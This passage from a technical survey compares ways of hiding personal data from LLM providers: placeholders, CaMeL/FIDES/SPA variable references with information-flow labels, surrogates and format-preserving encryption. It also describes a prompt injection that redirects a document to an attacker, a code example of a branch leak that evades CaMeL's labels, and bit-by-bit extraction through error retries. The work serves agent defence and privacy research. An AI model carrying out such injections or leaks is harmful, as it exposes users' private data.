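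*Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs* documents more of these changes. Models dropped one of the brackets around a placeholder or added a word inside the brackets, as in [YOUR_ADDRESS_1]. Some described the hidden data in words instead of using a placeholder. In replies to certificates that named only one organisation, a model referred to [ORG_2], which the software had never issued.

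A tolerant restorer can repair some of this damage. pii-guard, one of the existing tools in that test, marks values with tags that end in a slash. In one answer, a model left out the slash 29 times, and pii-guard's strict restorer lost all 29 values. A second restorer, which looked only for the type and number in each tag, recovered them.

Too much tolerance is dangerous because a wrong guess can insert another person's data. The software in *PromptGraph* (2026) restores a placeholder only if its identifier is in the mapping table and the entry passes further checks. It leaves anything else unresolved, even if it looks like a valid placeholder. This is clearly better for Maria's delivery, because if the planner wrote EMAIL_2 by mistake, an unresolved placeholder would stop the confirmation, while a guess might send it to a stranger.

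An early version of Beskorovainyi's engine mapped people with the same surname to the same placeholder, so a landlord and a tenant became one party and the restored text could name the wrong one. He considers this error worse than a leak because the user is unlikely to notice it. The engine now also compares first names, initials and gender, and gives an ambiguous mention its own placeholder.

### Measuring the round trip

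In *Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs*, Beskorovainyi tested restoration on 190 synthetic documents in each language. Two open models, with about 9 and 12 billion parameters, summarised each document and wrote a reply to it, giving 760 answers per language. His engine then restored the values, and he counted how many placeholders were restored correctly. He had set a target of 99% in advance.

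In UK English, the engine met the target, with one failure in 760 answers. The models altered 65 placeholders, and the engine restored all of them.

Russian was harder because names change their endings with their role in the sentence. A man's surname takes one form in a letter addressed to him and another in a sentence about him, so the engine has to inflect the name as well as restore it. With the worse of the two models, the engine restored 98.9% of all placeholders correctly but only 94.6% of those for names, and about a quarter of the answers contained at least one wrong name. Most of the 288 failures came from the inflection software that the engine borrows from pii-guard, which produced plurals such as "Kharitony" for Kharitonov. In another 82 cases, the engine had stored the name wrongly.

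These results depend heavily on the scoring. Beskorovainyi's earlier scoring programs accepted the plural as a form of the surname and would have put the Russian result at 99.8% or 99.9%. Even the final version does not check that each value returned to the right place. It also counts only placeholders that appear in the answer, so an answer that omits them all counts as having no failures. In a smaller test with pii-guard's tags and instructions, one model omitted all the placeholders in 25 of 40 answers.

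The test covered letters and summaries, not tool calls. A reader will usually understand a surname with the wrong ending, but a database search for it may find nothing.

### Eight techniques compared

Placeholders are one of several methods for keeping data from a model provider. *LLM-Redactor* (Agyemang, Kponyo and colleagues, 2026) compared eight of these methods on 1,300 synthetic prompts with 4,014 marked passages. The prompts were of four kinds: prose full of personal data, configuration files with passwords and keys, descriptions that identify someone without naming them, and company code.

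The study measured leaks for four techniques: answering simple requests with a small local model, replacing values with placeholders, having a local model rephrase the prompt, and adding noise by swapping random words for similar ones. A passage counted as leaked if the outgoing request still contained all of it or a piece at least four characters long.

| Technique | Personal data | Passwords and keys | Implied identity | Company code |
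|---|---|---|---|---|
| Placeholders, patterns only | 81.2% | 52.1% | 100% | 90.5% |
| Placeholders, with name recognition | 15.3% | 31.8% | 95.0% | 58.5% |
| The same, plus rephrasing | 13.9% | 31.6% | 94.1% | 55.8% |
| The same placeholders, plus noise | 17.6% | 30.3% | 95.0% | 51.7% |
| Local model where possible | 6.3% | 24.2% | 46.8% | 59.9% |
| Local model, placeholders | 1.2% | 6.3% | 44.5% | 38.1% |
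| Local model, placeholders, rephrasing | 0.6% | 6.4% | 43.6% | 31.3% |

Agyemang and colleagues recommend the combination in the last row. Its leak rate for personal data is 0.6%, mainly because the local model handled 94% of those prompts, so they never left the machine. Placeholders and rephrasing leaked 13.9% when every prompt went to the provider, and the same rate on the remaining 6% of prompts would give about 0.8% overall. The researchers did not test how good the local answers were. An agent that needs a strong planner for most steps would benefit much less from this combination.

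Rephrasing hardly reduced leaks and raised the median delay for personal data from 17 milliseconds to nearly two seconds. The noise had little effect because, at the default setting, it changed only about 1.8% of eligible words, so it usually missed the ones that mattered.

The other four techniques rely on special hardware or cryptography. A trusted execution environment is a protected area of the provider's hardware. It receives the full text, so its measured leak rate was 100%, and privacy depends on the hardware blocking the operator's access. In split inference, the user's machine computes the model's first layers and sends only intermediate numbers, from which an attacker can sometimes reconstruct the text. Homomorphic encryption lets the provider compute on encrypted data. Multi-party computation divides the data among several servers, which protects it only if the servers don't cooperate.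 Agyemang and colleagues list a leak rate of zero for the last three techniques, but only simulated them. Homomorphic encryption is 10,000 to 100,000 times slower than normal processing for all but small models.

Placeholders also made the answers worse. A small model answered 50 of the personal-data prompts with and without placeholders, and a judge model picked the answer to the original prompt as the better one in 78% of cases. Agyemang and colleagues call this loss of quality modest, which seems to understate it.

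The descriptions without names remained the hardest group. One mentions the finance chief of a particular company whose wife works for a competitor. Counting shared fragments is a poor test for such text, so the researchers used another model to check whether each of 20 samples still identified the person or organisation. It classified 19 of the 20 original texts as identifying, 19 after the placeholder swap, and all 20 after rephrasing.

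## Variable references: planning without reading the data

A variable reference hides everything a tool returns, whereas a placeholder hides one value and leaves the surrounding text visible. The planner writes a short program in which each tool's output has a name, such as `order`, and the executor runs the program without showing the planner what `order` contains. This hides Maria Keller's street address, even if no detector would have recognised it, along with the cello and the depot in Leeds.

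Researchers built these designs mainly to stop prompt injection. Hiding tool outputs from the planner also partly hides them from the planner's provider.

### CaMeL: the program comes first

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), separates writing a program from running it. The planner writes the program from the user's request and the tool descriptions before any tool runs. It uses a restricted form of Python, a language that models already write well. An interpreter then acts as the executor, running the program and calling the tools.

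Suppose Maria adds that the confirmation should name the neighbour who can take the parcel, which is in her delivery notes. The planner might write this:

```
order = find_order(email="maria.keller@example.org")
neighbour = ask_quarantined_model(
    "Which neighbour can take the parcel?", order.notes, output=str)
booking = move_delivery(
    order=order.id, address=order.address, day="Thursday")
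send_email(
    to=order.email,
    body=f"Dear {order.name}, your {order.item} will arrive on "
         f"{booking.day}. If you are out, the courier will try {neighbour}.")
```

The planner can write `order.address` because the description of `find_order` lists the fields of an order record. When the interpreter runs the look-up, it stores the record, including 14 Linden Street, in its own memory and later copies the address into the courier booking. The planner finished before the look-up, so its provider never receives the address. If the program runs on the first attempt, the provider receives Maria's email address once, in her message, compared with eleven times when the planner worked with raw data.

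The delivery notes are free text, so ordinary code cannot reliably pick out the neighbour. The program instead passes them to a quarantined model, which has no tools, and stores the answer in the variable `neighbour`, whose value the planner doesn't see either.

### Labels on values

Hiding data from the planner does not control where the data goes. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, describes a flaw that DeepMind researchers found in his earlier proposal. A user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's email address is in meeting notes. Anyone who can edit the notes can plant an instruction that makes the quarantined model return a different address. The document then goes to the attacker even though the plan is still correct.

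CaMeL therefore attaches labels to every value. As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain, the labels record where the value came from and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that checks the arguments and their labels and then allows or denies the call. Computer scientists call this approach information-flow control. The shop might label Maria's data like this:

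| Value | Source | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| `order.address` | Order database | Maria, the shop, the courier |
| `order.name`, `order.email` | Order database | Maria, the shop |
| `neighbour` | Delivery notes, through the quarantined model | Maria, the shop |

The policy allows the courier to read the address, so the booking goes ahead. If the program put the address into a ticket for outside contractors, the policy would block the call.

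A value built from several others inherits the restrictions of all of them. In Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, the permitted readers of a combined value are the intersection of the readers of its parts. For a text that contains both the address and the neighbour's name, this gives

{Maria, shop, courier} ∩ {Maria, shop} = {Maria, shop}

Trust works similarly, in that anything derived from untrusted data is also untrusted. A policy for `send_email` can allow untrusted text in the body but require a trusted recipient. That would stop the attack on Bob's document, or at least make the assistant ask the user before sending the document.

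With labels, ordinary software makes the decision rather than the language model. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), a study of agents dealing with people who try to extract private data, found that even a carefully specified procedure remained vulnerable when the language model decided whether it applied.

However, someone has to write and maintain the policies. Willison also worries that users who see too many approval requests will start approving all of them.

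### FIDES: one step at a time

A CaMeL planner commits to its program before it has seen any data. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, instead calls the planner again after each tool result, so the planner can base its next step on what has happened.

FIDES compares the label of each field in a result with the label of everything the planner has read so far. If a field would make the planner's context more confidential or less trustworthy, FIDES stores it in a variable. The planner reads the other fields. In Maria's case, it might see the order number and the delivery day, with `#find_order-result-0.address#` in place of the address. It can pass that name to `move_delivery`, and FIDES inserts the address when it makes the call.

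Sometimes the next step depends on hidden text. Suppose the shop must book a signed-for delivery unless a neighbour can take the parcel. The planner has the quarantined model check whether the notes name a neighbour and return a Boolean, either true or false. The software prevents the quarantined model from writing anything else. The planner then opens the variable that holds the answer, reads `true` and chooses the ordinary delivery.

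A single Boolean is too short to contain a planted instruction, so a policy can let the planner act on it even though it comes from untrusted text. But the answers to repeated questions can reveal much more about the hidden value.

The planner can also open a variable in full. FIDES then treats the planner's context as untrusted and blocks many later actions, such as payments. Costa and colleagues considered the restricted answers unnecessary for most of their test tasks and left them out, so the planner had to open variables to read the answers it needed.

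### Prudentia: telling the planner the rules

A FIDES planner isn't given the policies, so it may open a variable unnecessarily and then no longer be able to send an email. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) introduces Prudentia, a system built on FIDES in which the tool descriptions state the policy for each tool. Before opening a variable, the planner is supposed to explain why it needs the contents and list the calls it plans to make afterwards.

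Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse a piece of hidden text, which means declaring it trustworthy. If an email contains a list of ten tasks, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate actions.

Endorsement concerns trust rather than secrecy. Kolluri and colleagues considered a similar way to lift restrictions on private data, but chose to ask the user about each tool call instead because whether a disclosure is appropriate depends on the situation.

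### SPA: references that survive the request

CaMeL's variables exist only within one program, so if Maria wrote again on Friday because the cello had not arrived, a new program would have to look up her order again. In *SPA*, Girrens and Wang (2026) describe an agent that keeps its variables between requests.

Like CaMeL, SPA has the planner write a complete plan before any tool runs. The plan can contain only six kinds of step, such as calling a tool, querying the quarantined model or choosing between two branches. The plan is therefore simple enough for a checker to follow every label through it before it runs. If the checker finds a forbidden flow, SPA rejects the whole plan and ends the request without asking the planner to try again.

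After a successful request, SPA stores the results with their labels. On Friday, the planner sees a description of Maria's stored order record, including its fields, the reason for the look-up and the request that led to it. The planner can then write a step that retrieves the record. The interpreter loads the real values with their original labels, so contractors who could not receive an address on Tuesday still cannot receive it on Friday.

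In tests where an earlier request had stored a suitable result, SPA's planner retrieved it in 95.4% of cases without label checks and 89.9% with them.

### The cost in completed tasks

Researchers usually test these systems on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in four simulated settings: an office workspace, the chat service Slack, travel booking and banking. Its tools can return planted instructions, but the completion rates below come from runs without attacks.

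According to the latest version of its paper, CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. Independent tests gave much lower figures. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, ran CaMeL three times on the 16 banking tasks. With GPT-5.2, it completed 66.7% without policy checks and 37.5% with them. They also cite a test in which CaMeL completed 7 of the 21 Slack tasks with checks on. Even if it had solved all 60 workspace and travel tasks, its overall score with checks would be only 75%. The published runs must therefore have differed in the model, the policies or the treatment of blocked calls.

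| Design and model | Tasks | Completed without label checks | Completed with label checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, GPT-5.2 | Banking only | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| FIDES, o1 | Average of the four settings | 77.6% | 60.8% |
| SPA, GPT-5.4 nano | Single requests | 53.0% | 29.0% |
| SPA, GPT-5.4 nano | The same tasks, split into several requests | 62.5% | 35.3% |

The rows can't be ranked against each other because the models and policies differ. Within each row, most of the loss comes from the rule against acting on untrusted data. Many banking tasks require the agent to act on the contents of a bill or file, and planted instructions rely on the same behaviour.

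Garby and colleagues built their own agent, Randori, which completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 while its checks were on. Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, and its planner can mark particular data as trusted in advance, such as a bill the user has asked the agent to pay.

Prudentia's main measure is the share of tasks that an agent completes without human approval. With GPT-5, Prudentia reached 72.7% and FIDES 57.1%, while a basic agent that needs approval for every consequential action reached 35.1%. When a person approved every blocked call, Prudentia and FIDES were almost equal, at 80.0% and 78.9%.

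The benefit depends on the model. With the older GPT-4o, Prudentia completed 42.5% of tasks without approval, compared with 50.3% for FIDES. It also cost about twice as much, at roughly four to six US cents per task.

For privacy, the drop in task completion from hiding data matters more than the drop from the trust rule. An ordinary agent using o1 completed 84.0% of the tasks in the FIDES tests, so variables alone lowered the rate by about six percentage points. In SPA's tests with several requests, showing the planner the stored values raised completion by only 3.4 points.

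Both figures understate how much hiding data from the planner reduces task completion. SPA's planner still could not see new tool results, and the FIDES planner could open any variable. When Costa and colleagues removed both that ability and the quarantined model, completion with o1 fell to about 18%. CaMeL and SPA are closer to what privacy requires, because they keep the quarantined model but never let the planner open a variable. Without label checks, they completed 53% to 67% of the tasks in the table.

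### When the labels ignore the model provider

In the threat model for FIDES, attackers can tamper with data that tools read and can observe some tool calls, but they cannot see what the planner reads or writes. This treats the model provider as trusted, so in the tests FIDES hid only untrusted values from the planner. If the shop regarded its order database as trusted, FIDES with the test settings would show the planner 14 Linden Street.

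Prudentia can expose even more. Once its planner opens one variable without the user's endorsement, the software opens all the others too. This makes sense against prompt injection, because the planner has already read untrusted text and hiding the rest no longer gives it more freedom to act. But a planner that opened a single delivery note this way would also receive every other hidden value.

To protect Maria's data from the provider, the shop would have to treat the provider like any other recipient. It would leave the provider off the list of permitted readers for her address and check that list before sending any text to the planner. FIDES's general design allows this, since it can hide values for confidentiality and check a policy before each request to the model. The shop would also have to stop the planner from opening private variables, except perhaps to get a restricted answer such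 as a Boolean.

### The names in the user's own request

All these planners read the user's request as written. Maria's message contains her name, her email address and the remark about teaching on Tuesdays, and the planner copies the email address into its program.

The instructions that accompany the request can also contain personal data. In the FIDES tests, the planner's standing instructions included the user's name and employer, both invented for the benchmark. SPA includes the original request in the description of each stored result, so Maria's first message would go to the provider again on Friday.

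The shop can close much of this gap by using placeholders for the request and variables for everything else. Maria's program would then begin with `find_order(email=EMAIL_1)`. SPA would have to store the version of the request with placeholders, and the standing instructions would need placeholders too.

Detection is much easier here than in a redaction proxy, because the detector only has to check what the user types, not the long tool results. The remark about Tuesdays would probably remain.

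### The quarantined model reads the raw data

In Maria's program, the quarantined model reads the delivery notes, including the neighbour's name. If it runs at the same provider as the planner, the provider still receives the notes, in a separate request. Costa and colleagues used the same model for both roles, as did Girrens and Wang. Their defence against planted instructions still works, because it only requires that the model reading the notes cannot call tools.

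The remedy is to run the quarantined model on a machine that the user or the shop controls, so that the planner's provider never receives the tool outputs. The CaMeL paper, which Willison quotes, suggests that a smaller model might be enough because extracting data is probably easier than writing a plan. A small model may make more mistakes, though, and the planner could not detect a wrong neighbour in the confirmation because it never reads the notes.

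The shop can also use the quarantined model less often. The order record has separate fields for the address and the email address, so ordinary code can read them. If the shop has no suitable local model for the notes, it can replace the names in them with placeholders before sending them to an external model. The quarantined model would then return NAME_2, and the executor would replace it with the real name in the email. The shop then depends on a detector again, but only for the few texts that code cannot handle.

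### Branches, errors and loop counts

A program can reveal a hidden value through what it does, even if it never sends the value anywhere. Suppose it messages an advertising partner about a regional offer only if the customer lives in Leeds. The partner can infer from the message's arrival that the customer lives there, even if the message contains no address.

CaMeL blocks a direct version of this by applying a condition's label to the tool calls that depend on it. FIDES does not block it and guarantees only that private values do not flow directly into forbidden places. Costa and colleagues accept that someone who sees the sequence of tool calls may infer a little more. In their view, a stricter guarantee would essentially forbid publicly visible actions after the agent had read anything private.

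Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's protection has a gap as well. Adapted to Maria's order, their example looks like this:

```
elsewhere = True
in_leeds = True
if order.city == "Leeds":
    elsewhere = False
if elsewhere:
    in_leeds = False
if in_leeds:
    notify_partner("regional offer")
```

Maria lives in Leeds, so the program sets `elsewhere` to false, and CaMeL labels that variable as private. The program then skips the line that would change `in_leeds`. Because CaMeL updates labels only on lines that run, `in_leeds` keeps its public label and CaMeL allows the call to the partner. For a customer in York, `in_leeds` becomes false and the partner receives no call.

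A planner is unlikely to write such a program by accident, and planted text cannot make it write one, because the planner doesn't read that text. But the example shows that CaMeL's labels are not a complete guarantee. SPA avoids this leak by checking both branches in advance and, when a branch ends, discarding any variable set inside it.

Errors are a more ordinary risk. If a CaMeL program fails, the planner gets an error message and writes a new version. The failure may depend on private data. If the program fails because Maria's address has no postcode, for example, the provider learns something about the address. CaMeL censors these messages, but Garby and colleagues point out that each new attempt starts without the labels from the last one. Someone who controlled the repeated attempts could extract a secret one bit at a time.

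One solution is to find the mistakes before the program runs on real data. Randori's planner tests and revises its program on an artificial copy of the tools until it works. CaMeLoT, an extension of CaMeL by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the plan against the shop's rules before any tool runs. If the plan breaks a rule, the planner receives an example of how that could happen. The example comes from the plan alone and contains no customer data. Errors that appear only with real data would still need censoring, or the executor could end the request, as SPA does.

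Loops and timing can also reveal information. If a program contacts the courier once for each item in an order, the courier can count the items. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, suggest combining such calls into one or capping the number of repetitions. They also recommend that tools return success and failure in the same format, so that the program handles both the same way. To hide differences in running time, the executor can make every sensitive operation take as long as the slowest case, but Maria would then wait longer for her confirmation.

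## What a placeholder tells the planner

The software that hides Maria Keller's details has to leave something in their place, and that choice affects how well the planner can work. Her order record could reach the planner in any of these forms:

| Form | The record as the planner reads it |
|---|---|
| Deletion | Order 58213, one cello, [REMOVED], [REMOVED], [REMOVED], Tuesday |
| Opaque placeholders | Order 58213, one cello, MASK_1, MASK_2, MASK_3, Tuesday |
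| Typed placeholders | Order 58213, one cello, NAME_1, EMAIL_1, ADDRESS_1, Tuesday |
| Placeholders that keep structure | Order 58213, one cello, NAME_1, EMAIL_1@example.org, HOUSE_1 STREET_1, Leeds, Tuesday |
| Surrogates | Order 58213, one cello, Helen Marsh, helen.marsh@example.net, 27 Alder Road, Derby, Tuesday |

Deletion shows the planner only that three values are missing. Opaque placeholders are numbered, so the planner can match the MASK_2 in the record to the MASK_2 in Maria's message. Typed placeholders also show which of the three is an email address. The fourth version keeps two true details, the town and the email domain. Surrogates show the kind of value, but every other detail in them is false, even though they look the most informative.

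### Telling one value from another

Much of a placeholder's usefulness comes from its number. In *On the Impact of Anonymization on the Performance of Large Language Models*, Deußer, Hahnbück and colleagues (2026) compared five kinds of replacement on GPT-4o mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024. On MuSR, a set of long puzzles that take several steps of reasoning, the model scored 0.52 out of 1 when the same marker replaced every name, and 0.58 with labels that gave only a category, such as [CITY]. With numbered labels it scored 0.70, close to its result on the original texts.

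An average MuSR text mentions about nine people, places and other entities a total of 67 times. If every mention becomes [REDACTED], nobody can work out who did what. Part of the gap comes from the scoring, though, because the researchers' software restored the original names in the answers before marking them, which is impossible when several names share one label.

Random strings, such as Xj92Lp for London, did about as well as or slightly worse than numbered labels. These strings don't show what type of data they replace, so including the type in the label seems to have added little in these tests.

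Partial masking, which turns London into Lo\*\*\*\*, is a poor compromise. It reveals some of the real letters, and it can give two values the same placeholder, since Leeds and Leith both become Le\*\*\*. It did well on two of the three tests, but its score dropped on the third, which involves answering questions about retrieved documents.

Deußer and colleagues also tried telling the model that its input was anonymised, but neither a short notice nor a longer one made a clear difference. The notices did not explain what the labels meant, so a fuller explanation might still help.

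The punctuation around a placeholder has no clear effect on how often models alter it. *Reversible Pseudonymisation of Documents Sent to External LLMs* compares plain brackets, as in [PERSON_1], with longer tags that resemble web code, but two rounds of tests gave conflicting results.

### Naming the kind of value

The type matters more when an agent has to store information and find it later. Chen and colleagues tested this with three memory systems, LangMem, Mem0 and Memobase, which extract facts from conversations and retrieve them for later questions. GPT-4.1 ran the memory and wrote the answers. In the comparison below, the researchers kept the detector fixed and replaced the private passages with either three asterisks, an opaque placeholder such as `<Mask_1>`, or a typed one such as `<EMAIL_1>`.

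| Memory system and test | Unprotected | Asterisks | Opaque | Typed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| LangMem, MemPrivacy-Bench | 65.4% | 38.7% | 58.7% | 64.1% |
| Mem0, MemPrivacy-Bench | 68.6% | 26.8% | 63.9% | 67.9% |
| Memobase, MemPrivacy-Bench | 38.6% | 21.6% | 33.9% | 37.9% |
| LangMem, PersonaMem-v2 | 51.0% | 38.0% | 48.3% | 49.4% |
| Mem0, PersonaMem-v2 | 55.4% | 44.1% | 46.7% | 54.7% |
| Memobase, PersonaMem-v2 | 54.4% | 46.2% | 48.5% | 53.1% |

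Typed placeholders scored 1.1 to 8.0 percentage points higher than opaque ones in each of six comparisons, and never more than 1.6 points lower than no protection. On MemPrivacy-Bench, which has 615 questions, a four-point lead means about 25 more correct answers. Any single comparison is modest evidence, but all six favour typed placeholders.

The likely reason is retrieval. Suppose Maria once wrote "send the invoice to MASK_2". If the agent later searches its memory for her email address, little in that sentence would match, whereas "send the invoice to EMAIL_1" contains the word "email".

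The figures for asterisks exaggerate the effect of the missing information on the models' performance, because the researchers restored values only when they had used placeholders. When the correct answer was the user's email address, an answer with asterisks had to be wrong. PersonaMem-v2 is multiple choice, so an answer doesn't have to spell out a hidden value. Asterisks lowered scores by 8 to 13 points on that benchmark, compared with 17 to 42 on MemPrivacy-Bench.

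*Protecting Private Values in Tool-Using LLM Agents via Recoverable Context Projection* (2026) reports a similar gap for agents that work with health records. Between 44.8% and 59.3% of attempts ran successfully when the software used masks it could not reverse, compared with 87.5% to 92.3% when it replaced only the private passages and could restore them.

A poor detector can reduce accuracy more than an uninformative placeholder does. When GPT-5.2 chose which passages to hide, Mem0's accuracy on MemPrivacy-Bench fell to 32.2%, even with typed placeholders. Accuracy was about twice as high with opaque placeholders and Chen and colleagues' own detector.

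### Keeping part of the structure

For some tasks, the type is not enough. If a folder contains a Python script and a PDF, and the planner reads only PATH_1 and PATH_2, it cannot tell which one to run. SlotGuard therefore rewrites file paths piece by piece. Xia and Park give this example:

```
/Users/alice/acme/legal/layoff_bob.pdf
[REPO_ROOT_1]/legal/[SENSITIVE_DOC_1].pdf
```

SlotGuard replaces the longest opening part of a file path that it recognises as a trusted folder, hides other sensitive names and keeps a short remainder that the task may need. The planner no longer receives the names of the user and the company, or the information that Bob is about to lose his job. It still receives the information that the file is a PDF in the legal folder.

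SlotGuard replaces credentials with random fake keys in the same format, rather than with a label such as API_KEY. A label can lead a model to conclude that the key is missing, or it can break a command that expects a key in a certain format. When a tool needs the real key, SlotGuard swaps it in after some checks.

Xia and Park ran 200 workflow tasks with four models:

| Model | Raw data | Generic redaction | Typed placeholders | SlotGuard |
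|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 100% | 2.5% | 38.5% | 89.5% |
| GPT-5.4 | 100% | 2.5% | 20.5% | 98.0% |
| Kimi-K2.6 | 100% | 2.5% | 21.5% | 100% |
| Llama-3.3-70B | 93.5% | 2.5% | 31.5% | 93.5% |

With generic redaction, each model completed five of 200 tasks. The typed placeholders followed the rules of VibeGuard, an open-source redaction tool. They could later be replaced with the original values, but each one hid a whole path or key.

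In a second test, the models had to pick the right file for tasks from TheAgentCompany, a benchmark of simulated office work. They succeeded in 27% to 37% of cases with typed placeholders and in 88% to 95% with SlotGuard. The test did not cover the rest of each task, and its 160 cases came from just 40 file references.

Xia and Park also tried to separate the effects of the false keys and the path endings, using a small model and 12 tasks. The model solved ten tasks with the full version of SlotGuard and six when either feature was removed. It solved eight with ordinary typed placeholders, more than with either reduced version, which suggests that 12 tasks are too few to measure each feature's contribution.

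These results don't transfer directly to the cello shop, because the tasks are synthetic and concern file paths and credentials much more than customer records. A coding agent often has to build a new path from an old one or fit a key into a command, whereas Maria's street address only has to reach the courier unchanged, so ADDRESS_1 is enough. If the shop used a different courier for each town, the planner would also need the town, as in "ADDRESS_1, Leeds", to choose one.

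The provider can read any structure that the planner can use. From the example path, the provider learns that the company has a sensitive legal document. Xia and Park did not test whether a capable attacker could reconstruct hidden values from what remains visible.

Changing the form of the replacement also does not protect values that the software misses. In 200 sessions with 852 planted credentials, typed placeholders and false keys alone each leaked 23.5% of the credentials. The leaks came from keys that appeared in separate pieces. SlotGuard prevented these leaks by recording how each value relates to its fragments and later mentions.

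### Realistic false values

Before agents existed, medical researchers used surrogates to share patients' notes without revealing the patients' names. *CuratorKIT* (2026), a tool for preparing training data, follows their approach and gives each person the same false name throughout a sample of text. By default it leaves dates unchanged, because a contract with the wrong dates loses much of its meaning.

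Jathanna (2026) argues in *SurrogateShield* that surrogates are better than placeholders for both usefulness and privacy. SurrogateShield runs on the user's computer and might change "Sarah Mitchell" to "Ashley Wise" before a question goes to a chatbot. Jathanna compared it with Presidio's default labels, such as [PERSON]. Queries with surrogates were 94.9% similar to the originals, compared with 81.6% for queries with labels. A model acting as an attacker recovered none of 196 hidden values from the surrogate versions and three from the labelled ones.

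Both results depend heavily on how Jathanna built the tests. The similarity score, BERTScore, uses a language model to compare the words of two texts in context. Jathanna applied it to the original and rewritten queries, not to the chatbot's answers. One ordinary name is more like another ordinary name than like [PERSON], so the test favoured surrogates. If Maria asked which courier serves Leeds and the software changed Leeds to Derby, the query would still score well, but the answer could be useless. Jathanna leaves a study of answer quality to future work.

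The test compared two detectors as well as two forms of replacement. Presidio used its own detector, which treats any date as private, so it replaced some harmless text that SurrogateShield left alone. SurrogateShield replaced street addresses and organisations that Presidio did not. Jathanna did not test numbered labels or the setting in which Presidio inserts synthetic values itself. All 1,124 queries were synthetic, written by Claude Sonnet to a specification.

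The attack covered 100 of these queries. The attacker correctly guessed one name and two places from the labelled versions. If both methods were equally safe and the guesses independent, all three successes would still fall on the labelled side about one time in eight, so the difference could easily be chance.

Jathanna argues that even a stronger attacker would fail, because a surrogate has no statistical relationship to the value it replaces. But [PERSON] contains no information about the name either. The three correct guesses must have come from luck or from the surrounding text, which surrogates also leave in place. A surrogate does have the advantage that it may go unnoticed, while a label shows an attacker where to guess, but this helps less against a provider who knows that the names are false.

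SurrogateShield makes an exception for requests such as finding a pharmacy near an address. It changes the house number by two to eight and keeps the street, so the answer is still useful but the provider learns roughly where the user is. If the request mentions a sensitive subject such as abortion or domestic violence, it replaces the whole address.

### Encrypting a number into another number

Software can use format-preserving encryption to calculate a surrogate from the real value instead of inventing one. A secret key determines how each string in a fixed set, such as all 16-digit numbers, is replaced by a string from the same set, and no two strings share a replacement. A 16-digit card number therefore becomes another 16-digit number, and anyone with the key can recover the original without a mapping table.

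FF1, a standard method, does this in ten rounds. Suppose Maria's customer number is 204815. The software splits it into 204 and 815. From 815, the secret key and the round number, it calculates a random-looking number, say 467. It adds 467 to 204 to get 671, then swaps the halves, so the first round ends with 815671. If a sum has more than three digits, the software keeps only the last three. To reverse the round, it calculates 467 again using 815, which the round left unchanged, and subtracts it from 671 to recover 204.

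A card number encrypted this way passes the usual checksum only about one time in ten. If a tool or model verifies the checksum, the software can encrypt the first 15 digits and calculate the last one so that the number passes.

*Prϵϵmpt* (Roy Chowdhury, Glukhov et al., 2025) uses format-preserving encryption for values where only the format affects the answer, such as card numbers. In tests, the model answered every question about retrieved text correctly from the rewritten prompts.

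Ages and salaries need another method because their size matters. If a 50-year-old asks for a retirement plan, a random age of 17 would ruin the answer. *Prϵϵmpt* therefore adds noise that makes nearby ages more likely than distant ones. The guarantee behind it, called metric differential privacy, compares any two possible true values, *x* and *x′*. It limits how much more likely one of them can make a given output *y*:

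Pr[*y* | *x*] ≤ e^(ε·|*x* − *x′*|) · Pr[*y* | *x′*]

The provider can hardly tell an age of 50 from 51, but it may be able to tell 20 from 70. A smaller ε means more noise and better protection.

Encryption keeps the format of a value but not its meaning. *Selective Token-Level Cryptographic Redaction for Privacy-Preserving Clinical Deployment of Large Language Models* (2026) gives the example of "fever", which might become "4;cbP". The result still has five characters, but a model can no longer tell that the patient has a fever. The method suits numbers and codes better than names or symptoms. Encrypting a value with the same key also gives the same result every time, so an observer can see where the value recurs.

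Format-preserving encryption is poorly suited to short values. A two-digit house number can turn into only 100 different strings, and someone who learns which numbers a few of those strings stand for can narrow down the rest. The US standards institute NIST approved FF1 and a second method, FF3, in 2016. Its draft revision, *Methods for Format-Preserving Encryption* (2025), drops FF3 and requires a larger set of possible values for FF1.

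Every string of the right format decrypts to something, which creates a further risk for an agent. If the planner miscopied one digit of Maria's encrypted customer number, the executor would decrypt it to a different number, possibly another customer's, and would get no error. With randomly chosen surrogates and a mapping table, the miscopied number would probably not be in the table, and the executor could stop.

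### What a type label gives away

Suppose Maria's delivery notes mention that she can't lift the cello because of a back injury. With a typed placeholder, the planner receives the text with "a back injury" replaced by DIAGNOSIS_1. The provider can still learn that she has a diagnosis, though not which one.

A placeholder that contains API_KEY reveals that there is a key at that point in the text, which Xia and Park count as a separate kind of leak. In their credential test, all the typed placeholders disclosed the type in this way and none of the false keys did, although they warn that an observer may still infer the type from the format or context.

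An opaque placeholder has the same weakness. "She can't lift it because of MASK_4" still suggests a health problem. The shop would protect Maria better by replacing the whole reason with one placeholder, or by passing on only that she needs help with the parcel.

### When the planner believes a surrogate

A planner that reads ADDRESS_1 can recognise that the actual address is missing. If it reads "27 Alder Road, Derby" instead, it may reason from a false address. In Maria's case, the courier confirms that the cello will come from its Leeds South depot. Given the Derby address, the planner could conclude that the courier has confused two parcels, and cancel a correct booking.

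An invented name can also hide a relationship. Deußer and colleagues print an anonymised medical question in which "Azalea Kahler" replaces "his wife". The text given to the model no longer includes the fact that the woman is married to the patient, which matters in a question about infertility.

A surrogate can also match a real person's name. If the shop has another customer called Helen Marsh, and the detector misses her name in a support ticket, the software would wrongly change it to Maria Keller when it restores the original names. SurrogateShield never uses the same surrogate twice in a session, but this doesn't rule out a match with a real name.

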